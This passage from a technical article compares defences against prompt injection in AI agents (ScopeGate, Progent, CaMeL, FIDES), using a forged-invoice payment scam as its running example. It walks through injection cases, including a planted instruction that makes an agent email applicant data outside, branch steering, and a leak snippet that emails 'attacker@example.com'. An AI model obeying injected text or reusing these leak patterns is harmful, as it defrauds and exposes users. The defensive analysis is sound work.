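An attacker can do little with permission to buy the sneakers, because the description specifies the product, merchant and maximum price. The attacker might get the agent to pay $200 for shoes that another buyer would get for $180. If the permission is only to "make a payment", the attacker could get the agent to pay any account.

Zhu and colleagues acknowledge that MiniScope gives no guarantee if an attacker leads the agent to use another tool within the same permission, or the same tool with different values. They suggest that MiniScope could read the values in the agent's plan and, for example, limit a Slack permission to one recipient. They left this as an option because users who had to approve every recipient might stop reading the approval prompts. A limit chosen after the agent has read an attacker's message is unsafe, as with the ServiceNow ticket, because the "smallest"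 permission may be permission to contact the attacker.

### Both systems in the invoice example

In the invoice example, MiniScope would prompt the user for permission to read mail and make payments, and the user would grant both because the task needs them. The agent would then read the forged email and propose a $4,200 payment for A-999. MiniScope's checker would allow the call because it uses the permitted payment method. If a different email told the agent to delete the company's messages, MiniScope would still block the deletion.

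AP2 does not fit this payment exactly. Its first version supports payments that the merchant collects, such as card payments, while bank transfers are on its roadmap. But its limits on payees and amounts show what a mandate for the invoice could do, if account numbers identified the payees:

| Grant | Does it allow $4,200 to A-999? |
|---|---|
| MiniScope's payment scope | Yes, because the scope covers any payee |
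| A token from an exchange that narrows the scope to payments | Yes, for the same reason |
| A rich authorization request with the account number from the email | Yes, if the user approves it |
| An open mandate with a limit of $4,200 and no limit on payees | Yes |
| An open mandate with S-100 as the only permitted payee | No |
| A rich authorization request with S-100 from the company's records | No |

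The false invoice is for exactly what the company owes, so the amount makes no difference in any row. The outcome depends on where the payee's account number comes from. If the agent reads the email and then prepares a mandate for the user to approve, the trusted surface will accurately show a payment of $4,200 to A-999. A user who doesn't remember the old account may sign the mandate. If so, the wallet and the payment processor will find a valid signature and a payment that matches the signed mandate.

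If the company instead takes S-100 from its own records and signs the mandate before the agent opens the mailbox, the email cannot change the payee. The wallet will reject every payment the agent proposes to A-999, even if the supplier really has moved to that account. In that case, someone at the company would have to confirm the new account and sign another mandate to pay the supplier.

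## Payment agents: checking the values in every call

A mandate with S-100 as its only payee would stop the fraudulent payment in the invoice example. Without a mandate, the agent calls an ordinary payment tool, and the model fills in the account number and the amount. Software can still check those values against the company's rules before the call runs. This check is called per-call authorization. In June 2026 Mellafe Zuvic audited three common toolkits for building agents and found that none does this by default.

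### What the toolkits check

Mellafe Zuvic audited the public source code of LangChain and its companion LangGraph, LlamaIndex, and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which connects agents to the payment company Stripe. The audit used fixed versions of the code, so anyone can repeat it. It examined whether ordinary code compares the actual values in a proposed call with a policy before the call takes effect, and refuses the call if the values fail the check or the check itself breaks down. The audit did not include attacks on live services or the inside of Stripe's hosted tool server.

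| Toolkit | Version audited | What it checks by default |
|---|---|---|
| LangChain and LangGraph | Commits 00ad96c and bdb323e | The tool exists, and usually the values have the right types |
| LlamaIndex | Version 0.14.23, commit 520aa4e | The tool exists |
| Stripe Agent Toolkit | Commits 0b4961f and f54c9e6 | The action is on a fixed list and the API key's permissions cover it |

All of these are forms of tool gating. Once a tool is available, the toolkit passes on whatever well-formed values the model supplies. For Stripe, these include the amount, currency and customer. LangChain lets developers attach callbacks, functions that run alongside a tool call, but a callback cannot reliably block the call.

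To demonstrate the gap, Mellafe Zuvic built a LangChain tool that changes the account where a simulated merchant receives its money. The test submitted a call that set this account to acct_ATTACKER_999, and LangChain ran it. A similar test with LlamaIndex had the same result. Mellafe Zuvic wrote the call in advance, so the tests do not measure how often a model would propose it, though the comparison of 27 models suggests that many would.

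The toolkits' developers cannot know which accounts a company trusts. Mellafe Zuvic accepts that these are documented design choices that leave authorization to the agent's developer, and does not report them as vulnerabilities. A toolkit could still block a payment tool until the agent's developer supplies a policy for it. The Model Context Protocol leaves the same gap, since it has "no built-in point where policy is evaluated" before a call runs, according to Microsoft's *Securing MCP*.

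### What has changed since the audit

LangChain still leaves the check to the developer. LangChain's *Changelog* (2026) lists no release between June and September that adds a default check of values. According to LangChain's *Human-in-the-loop*, a developer can add a component that pauses calls to chosen tools for human review, and since version 1.3.3 the pause can depend on a call's values. A developer could, for example, pause only payments to unfamiliar accounts. But any tool the developer leaves out runs without review.

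The rule that decides whether to pause also has to return the same result both times it runs, because LangChain runs it again after the reviewer responds. If the second result is that the call needs no review, the tool runs even if the reviewer rejected the call. This could happen if someone added the account to the company's list during the review.

According to LangChain, version 1.5.0 introduced an optional component, still in beta, that uses a model to assess tool calls and blocks the ones the model classifies as risky. Claude Code's auto mode also relies on a model instead of a fixed rule.

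Stripe has changed more, but in its payment service rather than the toolkit. A company can now tag an API key as belonging to an agent. Stripe's *Set up two-party approvals* lists six actions, including refunds, payouts and outbound payments, that need a reviewer's approval by default when an agent uses a tagged key. Stripe's hosted MCP server has a similar confirmation step for agents that connect with a user's own login. Stripe planned for that server to refuse untagged keys from December 2026, according to its *Model Context Protocol (MCP)*.

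With these defaults, an injected instruction can no longer complete a payout without a person's approval. However, the reviewer may approve too readily, as Claude Code's users did. The agent can also attach a justification to its request, which raises the problem Hartman tried to avoid by keeping the agent's reasons away from the policy check. Companies can base a rule on the amount, who is acting or how often requests arrive, and they can also delete the default rules.

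The six default actions do not include changing a bank account, which is the closest match to the action in Mellafe Zuvic's demonstration. A company can add a rule for it. (Stripe's documentation is inconsistent here, because Stripe's *API keys* describes the defaults as covering changes to account configuration. It would be sensible for a company to check its own settings.)

A tool's name can also be a poor basis for deciding whether to allow a call. On Stripe's hosted server, the stripe_api_write tool can create a refund, cancel a subscription or edit an invoice. A gate that allows this tool by name allows all of these actions, unless the key's permissions exclude them. Stripe therefore bases its confirmation step on the action as well as the tool.

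### How ScopeGate decides

Mellafe Zuvic also wrote ScopeGate, a program that sits between the model and its tools and allows or denies each call. No model takes part in the decision. In the test with the changed payout account, the company's policy permits one account, acct_MERCHANT_001. ScopeGate makes its checks in this order:

1. **Tool.** The policy must list the tool. It lists the one that changes the payout account, so the check continues. ScopeGate would deny a tool with an unknown or misspelled name.
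2. **Permitted values.** If the policy has a list of permitted values for an argument, the value must be on it. The account acct_ATTACKER_999 is not, so ScopeGate denies the call here and the tool never runs.
3. **Amount.** For a payment or refund, the amount must be a finite number from zero up to a fixed ceiling.
4. **Idempotency key.** This is a label that lets a service recognise a repeated request and carry it out only once. If the policy requires a key and the agent's software has not supplied one, ScopeGate denies the call.
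5. **Default denial.** ScopeGate allows only calls that pass every check. It also denies the call if an error occurs during checking.

An early version had a bug in the amount check. It refused amounts *greater than* the ceiling, which seems equivalent to allowing only amounts within range. But computers have a special value called NaN, "not a number", for undefined results, and every comparison of size with NaN is false. Since "NaN is greater than 10,000" is false, the early version let the amount through. The corrected version allows an amount *a* only if it is finite and

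0 ≤ *a* ≤ *L*

where *L* is the ceiling. NaN fails this test, so ScopeGate denies the call.

ScopeGate denies any tool missing from the policy, but its published procedure checks only the amount and the arguments for which the policy has a list. If a developer adds an argument to a payment tool and forgets to write a rule for it, the model can put any value there.

The checks also work only if every call with real effects passes through them. If an agent can run its own programs and a credential broker adds the payment key to their requests, a program could bypass ScopeGate by contacting the payment service directly. Mellafe Zuvic suggests a central gateway for outgoing requests as one possible place for the check, which would prevent this bypass if programs had no other way to reach the payment service.

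### What the tests establish

ScopeGate blocked all 48 fixed attempts to bypass it, which included invisible characters in account names, look-alike letters and missing idempotency keys. Mellafe Zuvic also had the model GLM-5.2 attack it for 40 rounds and told the model why ScopeGate had denied each call. ScopeGate denied all 29 of the model's unauthorized attempts. Nine other rounds produced malformed output, and two produced harmless calls that ScopeGate allowed. In a separate test, it allowed all ten legitimate calls.

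If each set of trials were a random sample, the highest failure rate *p* compatible with no failures in *n* trials, at the 95% confidence level, would be the solution of

(1 − *p*)ⁿ = 0.05

This gives about 6% for the 48 fixed attempts, 10% for the 29 adaptive ones and 26% for the ten legitimate calls. These figures may still be too low, because Mellafe Zuvic chose the fixed attempts and a single model made all the adaptive ones.

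A better reason to trust ScopeGate is that its procedure is short enough to read. It checks whether an account number is on the list, and persuasive wording in an email doesn't affect that comparison. The bypass tests are mainly useful for finding coding errors like the one with NaN.

The test of legitimate calls is the weakest evidence. Ten successes do not rule out 260 wrongful denials a month at a company that makes 1,000 payments, which the company could not tolerate. The test also used a correct list, so it does not show what happens when the list is out of date. An outdated list is probably the most common reason a company would block its own payments.

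### Who writes the rules

An injected instruction can change the account in the model's proposed call but not the list that ScopeGate checks the account against. This protection would fail if the model could edit the list, because the email that led it to propose A-999 could also lead it to add A-999 to the list. Mellafe Zuvic therefore requires that no part of the policy come from a model's output, directly or indirectly, even if someone prepares the policy long before the agent runs. The policy also has to stay fixed during a conversation.

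This strict rule would exclude a supplier list that another agent compiled from last year's emails, since one of those emails might be forged. It would also rule out treating the saved recipients in a Stripe account as approved payees. Stripe's hosted server asks for confirmation before an agent sends money, but its documentation shows no such requirement for the tool that sets up a new recipient. An attacker could therefore use an injected instruction to get A-999 saved, and a reviewer who later saw it among the saved recipients might assume somebody had checked it.

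The rule is practical for an agent with one job, but a general assistant may need different permissions for every request, and nobody will write a policy by hand each time. In *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), a model writes the policy and ordinary software limits how the model can change it.

#### How Progent updates a policy

A Progent policy consists of rules about tools and the values passed to them, and blocks any call that no rule allows. In the paper's example, a user asks an agent to carry out the to-do list in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The task on the list is to summarize recent emails and post the summary to the user's Slack account, so the model that maintains the policy proposes to allow reading mail and posting to Slack. After the agent looks up the user's Slack name, the model narrows the Slack rule to messages for that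 name.

One of the recent emails contains an instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. This might fool the model that maintains the policy into proposing a rule that allows it. Let *A*(*P*) be the set of calls that policy *P* allows. Progent applies a new policy *P*′ automatically only if

*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

An SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical conditions can all be true, checks whether the new policy would allow any call that the old one did not. If so, the change needs approval. Permission to read mail was a legitimate expansion, but the approver could refuse an expansion that allowed sending email.

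*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) objects that Progent's guarantees depend on correct policies, and that hostile text in a tool's result may lead the update mechanism to relax them. The solver addresses the risk of relaxed policies, because a policy cannot become broader without approval. Before any model receives the tool's result, Progent also uses a model to decide whether an update is needed. But the solver compares each new policy only with the previous one, so it cannot detect that the first policy was too broad.

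#### What Progent's results measure

On AgentDojo, Progent reduced the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0% with agents running GPT-4o. On another benchmark, ASB, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Agents completed about as many legitimate tasks as they did without Progent. Progent also did better than AgentDojo's form of tool gating, which Shi and colleagues say is because that defence doesn't check values.

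In these tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically to simulate a careless user. The results therefore measure how well a model writes policies, not the solver's guarantee, which has no effect if nobody refuses an expansion. The first policy alone, which the model wrote from the user's request before the agent read anything untrusted, reduced the AgentDojo rate to 2.5%.

With human review, the rate on AgentDojo fell to zero. This depended on an ideal reviewer who never allowed payments to unrestricted recipients and always rejected an attacker's address. Shi and colleagues also left out two AgentDojo attacks that steer the agent toward a different legitimate hotel, because Progent does not try to stop misuse that stays within the permissions a task needs. Only 6% of policy updates were expansions, so a reviewer would have few decisions to make.

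#### When a narrower policy helps the attacker

Progent applies a policy update without asking anyone if the new policy allows fewer calls than the old one. In the invoice example, the user asks the agent to pay this week's invoices without naming any accounts, so the first policy might allow payments to any account. After the agent reads the forged email, the model might narrow the policy to allow payments only to A-999. Progent would apply that update, and the policy would then permit the fraudulent payment and block one to the real account, S-100.

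If the first policy allowed no payments, adding A-999 would be an expansion, and a reviewer would see it. So the outcome depends on how cautiously the model wrote the first policy.

*MasDrift* (2026) keeps everything the agent reads out of the policy. In one of its two designs, a separate agent uses the user's original request to write a fixed rule for every tool. Software then classes the values in each call as matching, mismatched or uncertain, and can allow the call, deny it or ask for confirmation. The forged email cannot influence the rules, but the user's request does not contain the right account number either, so the most the system can safely do is ask for confirmation.

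Progent gives companies that know their suppliers a more direct solution. They can write fixed rules that override the model's, such as one forbidding payments to any account outside their supplier list. The model could then narrow the policy further but not make it allow A-999. Protection against this payment would come from the company's list, as it does in ScopeGate.

### Tools with fixed values

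A company can sometimes avoid checking a value by not letting the model supply it, as in the single-customer tool that Ubl and Arora recommend for support agents. The developer's software could take the customer number from the customer's login and build it into the tool for that conversation, so the model could not enter a different one.

The Stripe toolkit has a limited version of this. According to Stripe, if a business manages payments for several connected accounts, the developer can set the account in the toolkit's configuration. The model still supplies the amount and other details of each request.

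For invoices, the company could replace its general payment tool with one that takes only an invoice number. Ordinary software would look up the supplier and the approved amount in the company's accounts and pay S-100. The model would not handle the account number. This works if the company has already recorded the invoice and someone has approved it, but not if the agent also copies the invoice details from the email into the accounts.

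Fixing the value is simpler than checking it and leaves less room for error, but it works only when the software can determine the right value without the model. For instance, a travel agent's customer may want the model to choose the hotel, so the company would have to limit the choice with a list of approved hotels or a maximum price.

### What happens to the invoice

Suppose the company in the invoice example gives ScopeGate a list of its suppliers' accounts, with S-100 for the regular supplier, and a payment ceiling of $10,000. The agent reads the forged email and proposes to pay $4,200 to A-999. The tool is permitted and the amount is below the ceiling, but A-999 is not on the list. ScopeGate therefore denies the call, regardless of how convincing the email was or which model the agent uses.

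Other calls are harder to judge:

| Proposed call | ScopeGate's decision |
|---|---|
| $4,200 to A-999, from the forged email | Deny; the account is not on the list |
| $12,000 to S-100 | Deny; the amount is above the ceiling |
| $9,000 to S-100 for goods that never arrived | Allow |
| $4,200 to S-100 for an invoice the company has already paid | Allow, if the software supplies an idempotency key |
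| $4,200 to S-100, with private customer data in the payment reference | Allow, unless the policy restricts the reference |
| $4,200 to A-999 after the supplier really has changed banks | Deny until someone updates the list |

#### Duplicate and false invoices

ScopeGate checks that a payment has an idempotency key, but not whether the software has used that key before, so the payment service has to detect repeats. It can do so if the company's software derives the key from the supplier and the invoice number, because a second payment for the same invoice would then have the same key. If the software creates a random key for each call, both payments will go through.

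Even a well-chosen key won't prevent a duplicate payment if an email presents the old invoice under a new number. To catch this, the company would have to compare each invoice with its orders and deliveries. A duplicate payment to S-100 benefits a dishonest supplier, and might benefit anyone who has taken over the supplier's account, but other outsiders gain nothing from it.

#### Free text

A payment reference or the body of an email can't be checked against a short list of permitted values. An injected instruction could make the agent copy private information into a reference that the payee will see. The company could limit the reference's length, require a fixed format such as an invoice number, or have ordinary software write it. These measures are of little use for an email that must answer a customer's question, so it is easier for the company to restrict who receives the email than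 what it contains.

#### New payees and upkeep

Somebody has to update the list when the company gains a supplier or an existing one changes banks, and an attacker may try to deceive that person instead of the agent. If a clerk sees that ScopeGate has denied the payment and copies A-999 from the email into the list, the agent's next attempt will succeed. The clerk should instead confirm the change with the supplier, and a second person should approve it. Stripe's approval system supports this second approval by preventing users from approving their own requests.

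The work of maintaining a list of approved payees depends on how often payees change. A company with 20 regular suppliers might update its list a few times a year, and its accounts department probably keeps one already. An online marketplace that pays hundreds of new sellers every week could not confirm each account by telephone. It would have to add sellers automatically after checking their identity, and an attacker who passed that check would become an approved payee.

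## CaMeL: tracking where each value came from

A list of approved accounts works for a company that knows its payees in advance, but many tasks need values that nobody could have listed. Software can instead allow or block an action based on where its values came from, which is called provenance tracking. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov et al., 2025) presents Google DeepMind's CaMeL, which combines provenance tracking with a program that the agent writes before it reads anything untrusted.

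### Planning before reading

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed dividing an assistant between two models. A privileged model has the tools and never sees untrusted text, which goes to a quarantined model that has no tools. If the quarantined model summarizes an email, the privileged model can tell the software to display the summary but gets only a reference to it.

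An instruction in the email then cannot add a step, but it can still corrupt an answer. If the quarantined model has to find Bob's address in a file, text in the file can make it return the attacker's address. Willison (2025), in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*, credits the CaMeL paper with finding this flaw in his design. CaMeL deals with it as follows:

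1. The privileged model receives the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and writes a program in a restricted form of Python.
2. An interpreter runs the program and calls the tools. It keeps the results in variables that the privileged model doesn't see.
3. When the program needs a fact from a text, the interpreter passes the text to the quarantined model, which returns a value in a fixed format, such as an email address.
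4. The interpreter labels every value with its sources and its permitted readers. (CaMeL calls these labels capabilities, though unlike Hardy's they don't themselves give access to anything.)
5. Before each tool call, a policy written as an ordinary Python function examines the tool, the values and their labels, and allows or denies the call.

Unlike an ordinary agent's next action, CaMeL's program *π* depends only on the user's prompt *p* and trusted information such as the tool descriptions *D*:

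*π* ~ *f*( · | *p*, *D*)

An email that the agent opens later does not appear in this expression, so it cannot put a new tool call into the program.

When the program computes a value *v* from *x* and *y*, the labels combine:

Sources(*v*) = Sources(*x*) ∪ Sources(*y*)

Readers(*v*) = Readers(*x*) ∩ Readers(*y*)

A summary of two documents therefore has both as sources, and only people who could read both may read it.

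### A document for Bob

In the CaMeL paper's own example, a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested at their last meeting, and says that the meeting notes contain his address and the document's name. A simplified program might be:

```python
notes = find_meeting_notes()
name = ask_quarantined("Which document did Bob want?", notes)
address = ask_quarantined("What is Bob's address?", notes)
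document = fetch_document(name)
send_email(recipient=address, attachment=document)
```

Suppose that the user, Bob and Carol can read the notes, but only the user and Bob can read the document. The values then have these labels:

| Value | Sources | Permitted readers |
|---|---|---|
| notes | Notes file | User, Bob, Carol |
| name | Notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob, Carol |
| address | Notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob, Carol |
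| document | Document store, notes file, quarantined model | User, Bob |

The decision depends on the policy for sending email. One possible rule lets the email go without asking the user to confirm only if the recipient's address came from a trusted source, such as the user's request. Another allows it if the recipient already has permission to read the attachment.

| What the notes contain | Rule about the address's source | Rule about the document's readers |
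|---|---|---|
| Bob's real address | Ask the user | Allow |
| An attacker's address | Ask the user | Deny |
| Bob's address, but the name of a different document that he may read | Ask the user | Allow |

Bob's address and the attacker's both come from the notes, so the source rule doesn't distinguish between them. The reader rule does, using the document store's own record of who has access. But people often request a document because they can't open it, and then the reader rule would block sending it to Bob too.

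### How FIDES differs

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a Microsoft system that uses similar labels but chooses one action at a time. An integrity label marks each value as trusted or untrusted, and a confidentiality label lists its permitted readers. If a tool returns untrusted data, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the planning model only the variable's name. The model can pass the variable to another tool or have a quarantined model extract information from it. It can also read the variable's contents, but then the whole conversation and any call the model chooses afterwards become untrusted.

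Costa and colleagues describe two basic rules. First, an action with consequences may run only if the choice of tool and all the values passed to it are trusted. Second, information may go only to people its label allows to read it. The second rule does not stop an injection from choosing an action, but it limits what an attacker can learn.

FIDES can also label how much information a value could convey. Suppose the agent has to check whether an email requests a meeting. If the quarantined model may answer only yes or no, the email can influence the planner by at most one bit, which a policy may allow. A choice among *k* options conveys at most log₂ *k* bits.

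| | CaMeL | FIDES |
|---|---|---|
| When the model plans | Once, before it reads untrusted data | Before each action |
| Protection without any policies | Injected text cannot add calls to the program | None guaranteed, because the model may open a variable and obey it |
| Protection with policies | Each call must also satisfy rules about sources and readers | Untrusted data cannot direct the actions that the rules reserve for trusted data |
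| Formal proof | None for the whole system | Calls do not directly copy private data to places where an attacker can read it |
| Outside the proof | Not applicable | What an attacker can infer from the agent's choice of calls, or from timing |

Costa and colleagues prove a property called explicit secrecy. They chose it over a stronger property that also covers inferences, because the stronger one would in effect prevent an agent from writing anything public after reading something private.

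### What the tests show

Debenedetti and colleagues wrote that CaMeL "effectively solves" AgentDojo, their earlier benchmark. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) report in *The LLMbda Calculus* that two injections were scored as successful in the original evaluation. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment described in a document, and the attacker had changed the document. The other was a scoring error. The agent quoted a hotel review, and AgentDojo's code wrongly counted the quotation as obeying the injection.

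FIDES also did well on security. With GPT-4o, 152 injections succeeded against an ordinary agent, 21 against FIDES with its rules off, and none with them on, after Costa and colleagues removed cases that AgentDojo had misjudged. The cost was in completed tasks:

| AgentDojo environment | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent, rules on | FIDES, rules on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
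| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

Hiding data in variables lets the agent complete many of the tasks that the rules would otherwise block, except in travel, where the rules seldom block anything and GPT-4o often mishandled the variables. With the reasoning model o1, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks.

In tests from 2026, CaMeL also failed to complete many tasks. In *CaMeLoT*, Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) ran it with Claude Haiku 4.5 and its policies on, and it completed 49 of AgentDojo's 97 ordinary tasks. Garby and colleagues found that it completed only 18 of 48 banking runs with each of two models, about half as many as with the policies off. The policies blocked every attack in their runs, whereas some attacks succeeded without them. *ToolFence* (2026) found CaMeL significantly slower than defences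 based on prompts or filters, partly because its programs are longer than an ordinary tool request.

CaMeL lowers task completion less when the models are better. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) tested five models on industrial maintenance tasks that several agents share. With the policies off, CaMeL lowered the completion rate by 21.6 percentage points on average, but by 13.4 for the two strongest models, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. The developer also had to describe the format of every tool's output, because the planner writes code to handle results it never receives.

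The strongest models also gain less from CaMeL on these benchmarks. Without CaMeL, 36.1% of attacks in a multi-agent version of AgentDojo succeeded against GPT-4.1, compared with 1.5% against Fable 5 and none against GPT-5.5. Peters-Gill and colleagues caution that GPT-5.5's result may reflect the limits of the benchmark's attacks, since determined testers have broken every leading model they tried.

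#### When one CaMeL agent instructs another

CaMeL's protection can fail at a handover between agents. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three CaMeL agents, with the policies turned off, and asked it to send Julie a summary of job applicants on Slack. The applicant database contained a planted instruction to send the data to an outside email address.

The database agent and the main agent both followed their programs. The main agent then included the summary in its message to a notification agent, whose planner treats such messages as requests from its user. The planner read the planted instruction as part of the request and added an email to its own program. Each agent had followed CaMeL's rules, but the notification agent's planner still treated untrusted text as trusted.

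Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each message into instructions, which may not depend on any tool's output, and labeled data, which the receiving planner cannot see. On the multi-agent version of AgentDojo, the average attack success rate was 12.9% without CaMeL, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and zero with multi-CaMeL. Each model faced 949 attacks in each setup, so the true rate for any one model with multi-CaMeL could still be as high as about 0.4%.

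### A legitimate step with an attacker's value

Fixing the program in advance limits which actions an agent can take, but not the values it uses in them. If the program sends a payment to an account number it reads from a file, whoever writes the file chooses the account.

Garby and colleagues analyzed the 144 combinations of task and attack in AgentDojo's banking tests. In 97 of them, the attacker needs a tool or file that the program for the user's task would not contain. If the user asks for a summary of recent transactions, for instance, an attacker cannot make the agent send money, because the program for that task includes no payment. In the other 47, the program contains what the attacker needs, so any protection has to come from the policies or from the quarantined model's resistance to injected instructions.

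Garby and colleagues built their own agent, Randori, on a small programming language whose label tracking they proved correct with the proof checker Lean. Randori's programs can *endorse* an untrusted value, which means deliberately treating it as trusted. The attacker succeeded in only two of 1,296 attacked runs. In both, the user had told the agent to follow the payment instructions in a text file, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without endorsement, Randori blocked this attack but could no longer do the legitimate task.

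Debenedetti and colleagues place such cases outside CaMeL's threat model. That is reasonable because CaMeL tracks where data comes from, and the user did choose the file as the source. But it leaves the user, who meant the file's original contents, unprotected.

### Tasks whose next step depends on what the agent reads

A program written in advance can contain branches, such as creating a calendar entry only if an email requests a meeting. But a request such as "do what's on my to-do list" requires the planner to predict what the list contains. Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most failures on legitimate tasks occurred because the need for another step became clear only after the program had started.

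A planner can defeat this protection by writing a program that lets a file choose which tools to call. When a user asked the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely, CaMeL's planner wrote a loop that could call any available tool according to the file. With the policies off, two attacks succeeded through this loop without the attacker adding anything to the program.

FIDES is more flexible because it replans after every action. But it has to open the file to determine the next step, and its rules then block most consequential actions. Costa and colleagues classed 44% of AgentDojo's banking tasks and 43% of its Slack tasks as dependent on data in this way, compared with 5% of office tasks and 10% of travel tasks.

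In *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too*, Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026), two of whom also co-wrote the CaMeL paper, reply that a planner can often predict what an agent will encounter. They adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen. The planner's programs averaged about 40 branches, compared with fewer than four on AgentDojo, and covered events such as a cookie notice or a failed click. On OSWorld, a benchmark of computer tasks, the system kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models.

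The additional branches also make the agent vulnerable to *branch steering*, in which false information sends the program down a branch that the planner wrote for another situation. Foerster and colleagues put a fake cookie notice inside an advertisement, and the agent clicked it and went to the attacker's site. Source labels are hard to use here because the same click could close a notice or delete a file. A later system, COBRA, checks web requests and MCP calls against limits that it sets for each branch in advance. It blocked 1,289 of 1,312 attacks in four benchmarks, according to *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks* (2026).

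### Leaks through branches and retries

Labels follow data as the program copies it, but a program can also reveal a secret by what it does. Garby and colleagues adapt a classic example, along these lines:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("attacker@example.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as private when a branch that depends on private data changes it. If the balance is high, "tmp" becomes false and private, and the program skips the line that would change "rich". The interpreter still treats "rich" as public and allows the email, which reveals that the balance is above the threshold. If the balance is low, the program sends no email.

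An attacker cannot insert this code, because the planner never reads the attacker's text. The leak requires a program that happens to contain such a pattern, so it is more a gap in CaMeL's guarantee than a ready-made attack.

CaMeL's retry loop leaks private information in another way. If a policy blocks a call because of a private value, the block reveals something about that value. Each result reveals at most one bit, but ordinary code outside the interpreter restarts the program after a failure, and the interpreter doesn't track what each failure reveals. Over repeated runs, twenty yes-or-no results are enough to identify one account balance among about a million.

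Peters-Gill and colleagues, who include CaMeL co-author Shumailov, accept the criticism about branches. Multi-CaMeL uses the same interpreter and has the same flaw, and they leave fixing it for future work. Multi-CaMeL does not retry failed programs, so it doesn't have the other leak.

### Who writes the policies

Debenedetti and colleagues write that prompt injection attacks "are not fully solved." They acknowledge that somebody has to write and maintain CaMeL's policies, and that users may tire of its requests for confirmation. Willison calls CaMeL the first credible defence that doesn't just add more AI, but he is nervous about any design that requires ordinary users to think about security policies. He hopes for well-chosen defaults and a clear interface.

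Some of this work can move to the people who write the tools. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes FIDES, an experimental feature in Microsoft's Agent Framework. A developer labels each source of data once and states what each sensitive tool will accept. If the developer forgets to label a tool, FIDES treats that tool's output as trusted and public, the less safe default. Once untrusted text enters the conversation, the rest of the run normally counts as untrusted, which can lead to unnecessary prompts.

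Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes similar experimental support in GitHub Copilot CLI, a coding agent, and in GitHub's MCP server. The server labels content from public repositories as untrusted and content from private ones as private. An agent that has read both is not allowed to post publicly, which would have stopped the Pacman attack. But the labels are crude, because everything in a private repository counts as trusted, even a customer's email that someone pasted there.

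CaMeLoT reduces wasted work by checking the program before any tool runs. In one example, a program would send a message to an address that the quarantined model had extracted from a chat channel. The checker rejects the program and returns the reason to the planner, which can then try again. CaMeLoT fully reproduces 22 of CaMeL's 28 security policies for AgentDojo. Most of the others depend on facts available only during the run, such as who can read a shared file.

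Labels can also make the remaining approval prompts more useful. Microsoft's sample policy for posting in a Teams channel allows the message if nothing untrusted influenced the call, or if everyone in the channel is already allowed to read the content. Otherwise it prompts the user for approval and lists the people who would gain access.

### The invoice example, with two different requests

Suppose the user asks the agent to pay this week's invoices and to take the account numbers from the company's supplier records. CaMeL's planner might write:

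```python
email = get_invoice_email()
supplier = ask_quarantined("Who is the supplier?", email)
amount = ask_quarantined("How much is due?", email)
account = get_supplier_account(supplier)
make_payment(account, amount)
```

The forged email contains A-999, but the program does not take the account number from the email. The lookup returns S-100, and the supplier receives the $4,200 it is owed. If the planner had mistakenly taken the number from the email, a policy that allows only accounts from the supplier records would have blocked the payment.

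That policy should require that the records themselves returned the account number. A rule against any payee with an email among its sources would block the correct payment, because the program used the supplier's name from the email to look up S-100, which makes the email one of the account's sources. FIDES could make the quarantined model choose from a list of the company's suppliers. With 20 suppliers, the email could then convey at most about 4.3 bits (log₂ 20). An attacker could still influence which supplier the company pays and how much, unless the software also checks the amount against an order.

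Now suppose the user says to use the bank details in each email. The planner replaces the lookup with a question to the quarantined model about the account number, and the forged email supplies A-999. The result depends on the policy:

| Policy for the payee's account | Genuine email with S-100 | Forged email with A-999 |
|---|---|---|
| It must come from the supplier records | Deny | Deny |
| It may come from an invoice email | Allow | Allow |
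| Ask the user if it comes from an email | Ask | Ask |

Every policy gives the same result for both emails, because the two account numbers have the same label. CaMeL supplies the kind of information about a payment's origin that Gallo's proof requires, but here that information is identical for the honest payment and the fraud. If the policy requires the user's confirmation, the prompt can at least show that A-999 came from an email and not from the company's records.

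More detailed labels could separate some of these cases. Costa and colleagues point out that mail servers can authenticate a sender's address. The company could therefore accept bank details only from an address at the supplier's domain. This would stop an attacker who writes from anywhere else, but not one who had broken into the supplier's mailbox, because that email would have the same labels as a genuine one.
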